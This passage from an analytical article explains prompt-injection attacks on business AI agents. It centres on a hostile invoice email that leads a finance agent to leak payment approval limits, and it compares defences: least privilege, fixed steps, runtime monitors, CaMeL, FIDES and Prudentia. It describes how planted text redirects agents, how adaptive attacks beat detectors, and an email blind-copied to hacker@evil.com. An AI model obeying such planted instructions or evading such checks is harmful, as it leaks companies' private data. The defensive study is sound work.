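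The researchers also have a commercial interest in alarming results. Tenable, Zenity, Capsule, Noma, Manifold, AppOmni and Cato all sell security products or services. Capsule published the two flaws it found as it announced $7 million in funding and launched its product, according to Help Net Security's *Capsule Security debuts with $7 million funding to secure AI agent behavior* (2026). Office 365 for IT Pros found Zenity's report "sobering" but is instinctively suspicious of such reports because so many are exaggerated.

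Microsoft's and Salesforce's fixes are good evidence that the flaws were real despite that interest, since neither company had a commercial reason to invent problems in its own products. The fixes are much weaker evidence of how often the attacks succeed. A researcher can choose a configuration that helps the attack, rewrite the planted text until it works and publish only the successful run. Tenable, for instance, doesn't report how many attempts its attacks took.

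### What each attack depended on

The table separates the effect of letting the agent choose its tools from the effect of letting it act without approval. The assessments of scripted flows are inferences, since the researchers didn't test scripts that did the same jobs. Where an approval step could have interrupted an attack, the person asked might still have said yes.

| Attack | Did it need free tool choice? | Did it need missing confirmation? | Would a scripted flow also have suffered? |
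|---|---|---|---|
| Travel agent, card data | No, repeated lookups were enough | Yes, but only approval by staff would have helped | Yes, if it didn't check who owned the booking |
| Travel agent, $0 trip | Partly, as the model chose which field to change | Yes, but only approval by staff would have helped | Only if it let customers edit the price |
| Copy of McKinsey's agent | Yes | Yes, for the reply | No, if the reply used a template with fixed fields |
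| ShareLeak | Yes | Yes, for the email | No, if it only recorded the form entry |
| PipeLeak | Yes | Yes, for the email | No, if it read only the new lead |
| SalesBleed | Yes, to query other records | Not for email, as the data left by another route | No, if it read only the new lead |
| Azure DevOps | Yes | Yes, in the set-up that Manifold tested | No, if it stayed within the project under review |
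| ServiceNow | Yes, including the choice of a second agent | Yes, for the second agent's actions | No, if it had no step that called the second agent |

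## What limits the damage when no one approves each step?

In the hostile invoice run, an email led the finance agent to look up the company's payment approval limits and send them to a stranger. The theft depended on a policy file that contained those limits, an email tool that could send anything to anyone, and a planning model that read the stranger's text. A company can change each of these without asking a clerk to approve every call. Some changes take a few minutes in the agent's settings, while others require redesigning the agent.

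### Fewer tools and narrower credentials

Under the principle of least privilege, a program gets only the access its job requires. The finance agent needs all three of its tools but not the whole policy file, because it has to tell customers when the company pays, not who can approve a payment. If the maker moves the approval rules into a separate file and leaves that file unconnected, the agent can't find them, even if the hostile email gets it to search.

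The record tool could likewise run under an account that can add invoices but can't change addresses or delete anything. If an email led the model to propose a new billing address, the database would reject the change. The maker has to set this up, because an agent with an event trigger may otherwise run with the maker's own, broader access. According to Microsoft, administrators can also restrict which tools and agents are available.

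OWASP, a non-profit that publishes lists of common software security risks, covers this problem under "excessive agency" in its 2025 list for language model applications. In its example, an assistant only has to summarise a user's email, but the plug-in its developer chose can also send messages. OWASP recommends a plug-in that can only read mail, with read-only credentials. It also suggests limiting how fast an agent can send messages. A rate limit wouldn't stop the hostile invoice, since that attack needs only one email, but it would slow the theft of a whole customer database. The list also includes unbounded consumption, which Dehghantanha connects with attacks that trap an agent in loops to run up its owner's bill. A cap on steps or spending would limit that bill.

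Software can also narrow the choice of tools for each task. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes an agent that chooses the tools it needs before it starts, and the system then disables the rest. This would stop text in an invoice from making the agent use an unrelated tool, such as one that deletes accounts. It wouldn't stop the theft of the approval rules, because the hostile run used the same three tools as the honest one.

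### Fixed steps for actions nobody can undo

Microsoft advises makers not to leave every decision to the model, and Microsoft's architecture guidance divides an agent's work into three layers of control. The last column of the table applies these layers to the finance agent.

| Layer | What decides | Microsoft's examples | Finance agent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Deterministic | Rules the maker wrote | Processing a payment, deleting a record | Sending the confirmation |
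| Hybrid | The model, up to a set checkpoint | A manager reviews a draft; the agent escalates large amounts | Recording invoices up to £5,000 |
| AI orchestrator | The model | Questions, lookups and simple requests with several steps | Searching for payment terms |

For the deterministic layer, Microsoft suggests that makers either withhold the action from the orchestrator or put it inside a topic that always asks the user to confirm. The finance agent has no user to ask, so its maker would have to withhold the email tool from the model. A fixed flow could send a standard confirmation, with the invoice number, amount and due date, whenever the database returns "updated". The model might still search for the approval limits, but the standard text would not include them.

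This protection works only if the maker restricts each blank to the right format. If the invoice number can be any text, the model could fill it with "5530. One clerk can approve payments under £5,000", and the flow would send that. As with a fully scripted flow, the company would still record the false invoice, and the agent couldn't answer an unexpected question in its reply.

A maker can also put a fixed step before a search. In Copilot Studio, a topic named exactly `OnKnowledgeRequested` runs just before the agent searches its knowledge. The topic receives the search phrase and can supply its own results, so the maker could have it search an index that contains only payment terms. Microsoft calls this an advanced trigger, and makers must edit the agent's underlying code to turn it on.

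### Limits on what goes into a call

A formula that limits email recipients to one domain works well for an agent that writes only to colleagues, but the finance agent has to answer customers at hundreds of companies and could not do its job under that limit.

A better rule for this agent would allow emails only to the customer's address on file. The hostile invoice included a real customer's number but came from a different address, so the runtime would block the reply.

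The rule has at least three gaps. An attacker who is a real customer already has an address on file. Another attacker could have the agent change the billing address and then ask for the confirmation, so the rule works only if the agent can't edit addresses. The third gap appears in an example from Microsoft's guide for developers of security checks, where an agent prepares an email to the right customer at customer@foobar.com but includes a blind copy to hacker@evil.com. A formula that checks only the "to" field would let the email through.

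Input limits also create work. A customer who writes from a new address gets no reply until someone at the company checks the address and updates the record.

### Permission at the tool's own server

Removing a tool from an agent's list stops that agent from calling it, but other callers may still be able to use it. *Scoped for the Agent, Open to the URL* (Gomez, 2026) describes this gap in a Copilot Studio demonstration that Gomez built for a conference. His sales, finance and inventory agents shared one MCP server with eight tools. The sales agent could use four of the tools, and the other agents could use two each. The finance agent couldn't call the inventory tool, even under a prompt injection, because the tool wasn't on its list.

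Gomez found code enforcing these limits only on the agents' side. The server checked no password, token or identity. He had also opened it to the internet through an anonymous connection, so anyone with the address could have called all eight tools. He blames his own set-up, not Copilot Studio, because he had treated a list of tools as if it controlled access to the data.

The remedy is for the server to check each caller's rights. Gomez points to Microsoft's SQL MCP Server, which can set access rules for each table and field and applies them to every tool. Such rules could let the finance agent create invoices but not change addresses. They are especially important because the server's standard tools are generic. For example, `read_records` reads any table the company has exposed, so we can tell little about what an agent can see from its permission to use that tool. A company can instead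 offer a narrow database procedure as a separately named tool.

OWASP also recommends that the system behind the tool authorise each request, rather than rely on a model to decide what is allowed. This check cannot separate malicious searches from legitimate ones, because both arrive under the same identity. If the finance agent may read the approval rules, the server will return them regardless of what prompted the search.

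### A security check before every call

A runtime check tries to catch that difference by examining why the agent wants to make a call. Microsoft Defender can do this for Copilot Studio, and it checks topics and knowledge searches as well as tool calls. For the hostile invoice's first call, the exchange might look like this, in simplified form:

```
sent to the checking service
  context:          details of the triggering email
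  thought:          "The sender wants to know who approves payments"
  previous outputs: none
  tool:             search_policy, with its description and inputs
  input values:     "who can approve payments, and up to what amount"
  metadata:         the agent, the trigger, the plan and the step

returned
  blockAction:      true
  reason:           "The search is unrelated to the invoice"
```

The "thought" is the orchestrator's explanation for choosing the tool. The response must include a true-or-false answer and can include a reason. Companies can connect another supplier's service or write their own, as long as it answers in this format.

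If the answer is to block, the agent stops processing and tells the user that it has blocked the message, according to Microsoft's set-up instructions. In the invoice scenario, Microsoft's security researchers describe an entry in the agent's activity history and an alert for the security team. The alert matters more here because no user is present. But Microsoft's *Protect your environment in real-time during agent runtime* warns that the alerts don't appear in the Defender portal if the company hasn't connected its Microsoft 365 account to Defender, although the blocks still work.

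The check runs again before the agent sends the email, so Defender can still catch the theft if it misses the search. By then, both the earlier outputs and the proposed message contain the approval rules, which makes the theft easier to recognise.

If the checking service is slow or broken and doesn't answer within one second, the agent by default proceeds as if it had received permission. Administrators can choose to block the call instead, but then a fault in the service may also stop legitimate invoices. A company that relies on this check for an unattended agent should probably accept that risk, because a delayed invoice is easier to fix than a leaked document.

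Microsoft planned to make these external checks generally available on 10 December 2025, according to a notice that itelio republished. Trent's *Runtime Protection for Agents* describes a later extension of the checks to the tool servers that companies register with Agent 365, Microsoft's system for managing agents. On those servers, Defender can examine a tool's response as well as the call, so it could catch instructions planted in the response before the model acts on them.

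### How well do runtime checks work?

Microsoft describes three scenarios in which Defender blocks the attack, but neither that account nor the product's documentation gives a detection rate or a false alarm rate. The scenarios show what the check is for, but a company would have to run its own test attacks to find out how often it works.

Defender also receives the agent's explanations and earlier tool results, which Anthropic withholds from the automated approver in Claude Code. This gives Defender more evidence, but an attacker can influence all of it. If a checking service uses a language model to read that material, the attacker can try to manipulate the checker too. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) points out that OWASP's guidance warns of this.

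Independent tests of other defences give reason for caution. Narisetty and colleagues summarise work by Nasr and others on twelve published defences, most of which had attack success rates near zero when first reported. Attackers who knew the defence and adapted to it succeeded more than 90 per cent of the time against most of the twelve. The defences they beat included PromptGuard and Model Armor, two products that screen text for attacks. Another detector separated attacks from harmless text perfectly on standard benchmarks but missed 69 per cent of attacks on a different set. A simple adapted attack got past it every time. None of these tests covered Defender, which examines proposed calls as well as text, so the percentages don't apply to it.

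A check can also apply explicit rules instead of trying to recognise an attack. Progent, a research system, compares each tool call and its inputs with rules such as "send email only to an address on file". A language model can help write the rules, but ordinary software applies them. Its developers reported that Progent cut the attack success rate from 39.9 to 1.0 per cent on AgentDojo, the simulated office, bank and travel agency described earlier.

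Narisetty and colleagues repeated the test with Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, and averaged three runs. Progent reduced attack success from 25.8 to 4.2 per cent. When they rewrote the attack with Progent in mind, the rate was 2.6 per cent, so adapting didn't help the attacker. The evidence is encouraging but limited, because they tested only one weak model and one handwritten attack template. They left stronger attacks, optimised by computer against the model, for later work.

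The source of the rules matters as much as their enforcement. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026) describes defences in which a second model derives the rules from the user's request. The finance agent has no user, so its rules would have to come from its maker. If its software treated the incoming email as the request, the attacker would help write the rules.

### Planning before reading the email

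All the measures so far leave the planning model exposed to untrusted text. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues propose a stricter principle that once an agent has taken in untrusted content, that content must be unable to trigger a consequential action. In December 2025, the UK's National Cyber Security Centre similarly advised developers to concentrate on conventional safeguards that limit what a system can do, and not just on keeping malicious text away from the model.

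The simplest design that follows the principle fixes the plan before the agent reads anything untrusted. In an example from Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, a user asks an assistant to send today's schedule to his boss, John Doe. The assistant commits to two calls, reading the calendar and emailing John Doe. Instructions hidden in a calendar entry can't add a third call or change the recipient.

The finance agent could plan the same way, using only the maker's instructions and the fact that an invoice has arrived. Its plan would contain a search for "payment terms for invoices", an update and a reply. The hostile email could then no longer cause a search for approval limits, because the model would have written the query before seeing the email.

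The plan-first designs described earlier write their steps after reading the request. If the request is a hostile email, the attacker influences the plan before the software locks it. Copilot Studio's original plan-first approach therefore doesn't protect against a hostile email that arrives in the trigger's message.

Even a plan made before the agent reads outside content fixes only the steps. The calendar entry can still change everything the message says, though not who receives the schedule. The invoice email can still supply a false amount, another company's customer number or a misleading due date, because the agent has no other source for those values. If the model writes the reply after reading both the email and the policy search results, the reply may also include any private text the search returned.

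### Separating the planner from the reader

CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and others presented in 2025, deals with part of this problem by using two models and a program. The planning model has access to tools but never reads untrusted text. The reading model handles untrusted text but has no tools. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) outlines the procedure, which runs as follows:

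1. The planning model receives only the trusted request and writes a program that will carry it out.
2. An interpreter, a piece of conventional software, runs the program one line at a time.
3. When the program needs a fact from untrusted text, the interpreter gives the text to the reading model and stores the answer in a variable. The planning model never sees the answer.
4. The interpreter records where each value came from and who may read it. Values computed from others inherit their restrictions.
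5. Before each tool call, the interpreter compares the inputs and their records with the security policy, and refuses a call that breaks it.

For the finance agent, the maker's standing instructions would have to serve as the trusted request. The program might be:

```
invoice = reader("extract customer, number, amount and date", email)
terms   = search_policy("payment terms for invoices")
due     = reader("work out the due date", invoice, terms)
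update_customer_record(invoice.customer, invoice.number,
                       invoice.amount, due)
send_email(to = email.sender, body = template(invoice.number, due))
```

The planted instructions now reach only the reading model, which can't search or send anything. On the third line, they could still make the reading model put approval limits in `due` instead of a date, if the search returned a passage that mentions those limits. But the interpreter would have recorded that `due` came partly from the policy file. If the policy reserves that file for staff, the interpreter blocks any email that would send the value to an outsider.

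It would refuse the legitimate confirmation too, because a genuine due date also comes partly from the policy file. The maker has to mark the payment terms as suitable for customers and keep the approval rules restricted. CaMeL can enforce such distinctions, but someone at the company has to define them correctly for every source the agent reads.

According to Narisetty and colleagues, CaMeL completed 77 per cent of AgentDojo tasks under attack with OpenAI's o3 model, compared with 84 per cent for the same model without the defence. None of the injection attacks that CaMeL is meant to stop succeeded. It used about 2.8 times as many input tokens and 2.7 times as many output tokens. A company would also have to rewrite an existing agent to use it.

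### Labels that follow the data

Microsoft researchers took a related approach in FIDES, which keeps the usual step-by-step loop but labels everything that passes through it. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, give each piece of data two labels. One records whether it is trusted or untrusted, and the other lists who may read it. When the agent combines data, the result takes the stricter label:

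```
trusted + untrusted                        = untrusted
{clerks, customers} + {clerks, directors}  = {clerks}
```

Costa and colleagues pair the labels with two rules. The agent may take a consequential action only if it based the decision on trusted data, and it may send information only to people whom the label allows to read it. If the finance agent wrote a message from payment terms that customers may read and approval rules that only clerks and directors may read, only clerks could receive it. The second rule limits what information an attacker can extract, but it doesn't stop the attacker from influencing the agent.

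FIDES hides untrusted results in variables to keep the planning model's context trusted. The model can pass a variable to a tool without reading it. If it opens the variable, its context becomes untrusted and the rules block most later actions. It can also ask an isolated model a question about the contents, which that model must answer in a fixed format. A yes-or-no answer to "Is this an invoice?" carries only one bit, so an attacker can use a hostile email to force the wrong answer but can't pass an instruction through it. The attacker could have got the same "yes" by sending a real invoice.

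With suitable rules, FIDES stopped every attack in AgentDojo. Using OpenAI's o1 model, it completed 16 per cent more tasks than a basic agent under the same kind of strict enforcement, and 8 per cent more with GPT-4o. When the researchers switched enforcement off, the extra machinery reduced task completion by 6.3 per cent compared with the basic agent. FIDES therefore recovers much, but not all, of the usefulness lost to strict rules.

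Labels can be stricter than a maker expects. If the software uses a customer number from the email to look up the address on file, the address becomes untrusted too, even though the sender didn't write it. The maker could have the isolated model pick the number from a fixed list of customers, and let the rules accept that choice because it carries so little information. An attacker could still make the model pick the wrong customer.

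The guarantees also depend on correct initial labels. Costa and colleagues normally treat the user's message as trusted. Copilot Studio delivers an event's details to the agent as a message, so a developer who added FIDES and kept that default would label the hostile email as trusted and lose the protection. Narisetty and colleagues note a similar danger in the deployed version of FIDES, which treats unlabeled data as trusted. Neither FIDES nor CaMeL protects against poisoned tool descriptions, because both assume the descriptions are honest.

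Some information can escape without appearing in any message. If the agent replied at once to invoices that one clerk can approve and held back the rest, an outsider could send invoices of different sizes and work out the approval limit from the timing of the replies. Costa and colleagues don't claim that FIDES prevents leaks through the agent's choice of actions. They argue that preventing them would mean forbidding almost every visible action after the agent reads something private.

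### When the next step depends on what the email says

The main objection to planning in advance is that many tasks don't allow it. A user who asks an agent to complete today's to-do list wants it to read the list and then decide what to do. Costa and colleagues define the difference precisely. Let S(d) be the set of action sequences, including the final reply, that solve a task when the data are d. The task is data-independent if at least one sequence belongs to S(d) for every possible d:

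⋂ S(d) ≠ ∅

Recording an ordinary invoice meets this condition because the same steps work for any amount, as long as the program passes the values in variables. Handling an email that disputes a charge, gives a new address and requests an old statement does not meet it, because another customer's email would need different steps. A planner can write a branch for a predictable problem such as a missing purchase order number, but not for every request a customer might make.

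*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026), a successor to FIDES by several of the same researchers, accepts that CaMeL's plan can't depend on what its tools return, and reports that designs of this kind have reduced task completion on AgentDojo by up to 30 per cent. It argues that the usual comparison with an undefended agent is unfair, because that agent looks more capable only if it can act without restriction, and many real products require a person to approve each consequential call. A system that tracks data needs approval only when a call breaks its rules.

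They therefore count how many tasks an agent completes with at most k approvals per task. If vᵢ is the number of calls in task i that would need approval, the measure is

TCR@k = (number of tasks completed with vᵢ ≤ k) ÷ (number of tasks)

At k = 0, the agent works entirely unattended. The table gives their AgentDojo results with OpenAI's o3-mini. Their new agent, Prudentia, tells the planning model about the labels and rules so that the model can avoid breaking the rules.

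| Agent | Tasks completed without approval | Approvals across all completed tasks |
|---|---|---|
| Approval for every consequential call | 24.3% | 48.2 |
| The same agent with labels | 35.5% | 32.4 |
| FIDES | 50.1% | 18.8 |
| Prudentia | 59.1% | About 17 |

Prudentia can also ask a person to endorse untrusted data instead of approving each action that follows from it. If a harmless email lists ten tasks, one endorsement replaces ten approvals. In a separate test with simulated GitLab and Reddit sites, Prudentia needed no approvals and no attack succeeded. However, those tasks only involved posting a comment or upvoting a post, so the agent never had to open the untrusted text.

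This reply addresses the complaint about cost better than the complaint about flexibility. More than 40 per cent of the AgentDojo tasks still failed or needed a person, although newer models may do better than o3-mini. Kolluri and colleagues also assume that the person stops every harmful call, but Anthropic found that testers approved most of the dangerous commands. Each decision matters more with endorsement, because a clerk who endorsed the hostile invoice without seeing its hidden text would turn the attacker's instructions into trusted data, and the agent could then follow them without asking again.

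Labels also do not prevent ordinary mistakes. Kolluri and colleagues say their design can replace human approval as a defence against attacks, but not as a check on a model that misunderstands its task.

### Which measures suit the invoice agent?

For an agent that mostly records invoices, a separate file for the approval rules and a fixed confirmation email would stop this theft with few drawbacks. CaMeL and FIDES are more worthwhile when an agent has to write free text to outsiders using private sources, since no template can cover every reply. None of the measures in the table establishes that the £960 invoice is genuine, so the company still needs to match it with a purchase order or a delivery.

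| Measure | What it stops in the hostile invoice run | Gap left | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fewer tools, less data, narrower credentials | The search finds no approval rules | Misuse of whatever access the agent still needs | Separate files and accounts to maintain |
| Fixed steps for irreversible actions | The confirmation has no place for stolen text | False values in the blanks | The agent can't answer unexpected questions in its reply |
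| Limits on inputs | The email can't go to an address that isn't on file | Attackers with an address on file; fields the rule doesn't cover | Staff must handle new addresses |
| Authorisation at the tool's server | The server refuses data and changes outside the agent's rights | Hostile requests within those rights | Access rules for each table and field |
| Runtime check, such as Defender's | The service may block the search or the email | Missed attacks; late answers count as permission by default | Set-up, data sharing and false alarms |
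| Plan fixed before reading | The email can't add a search or change the query | False values and altered message text | Tasks that need a new plan after reading |
| Separate planner and reader (CaMeL) | Restricted text can't go to an outsider | False values; wrong records of who may read what | 77% of tasks completed instead of 84%, about 2.8 times the tokens, and a rewritten agent |
| Labels on all data (FIDES, Prudentia) | Untrusted text can't prompt a consequential action, and restricted text can't leave | Wrong labels, careless endorsements and leaks through the choice of actions | Labels and rules to maintain, and approval for some tasks |
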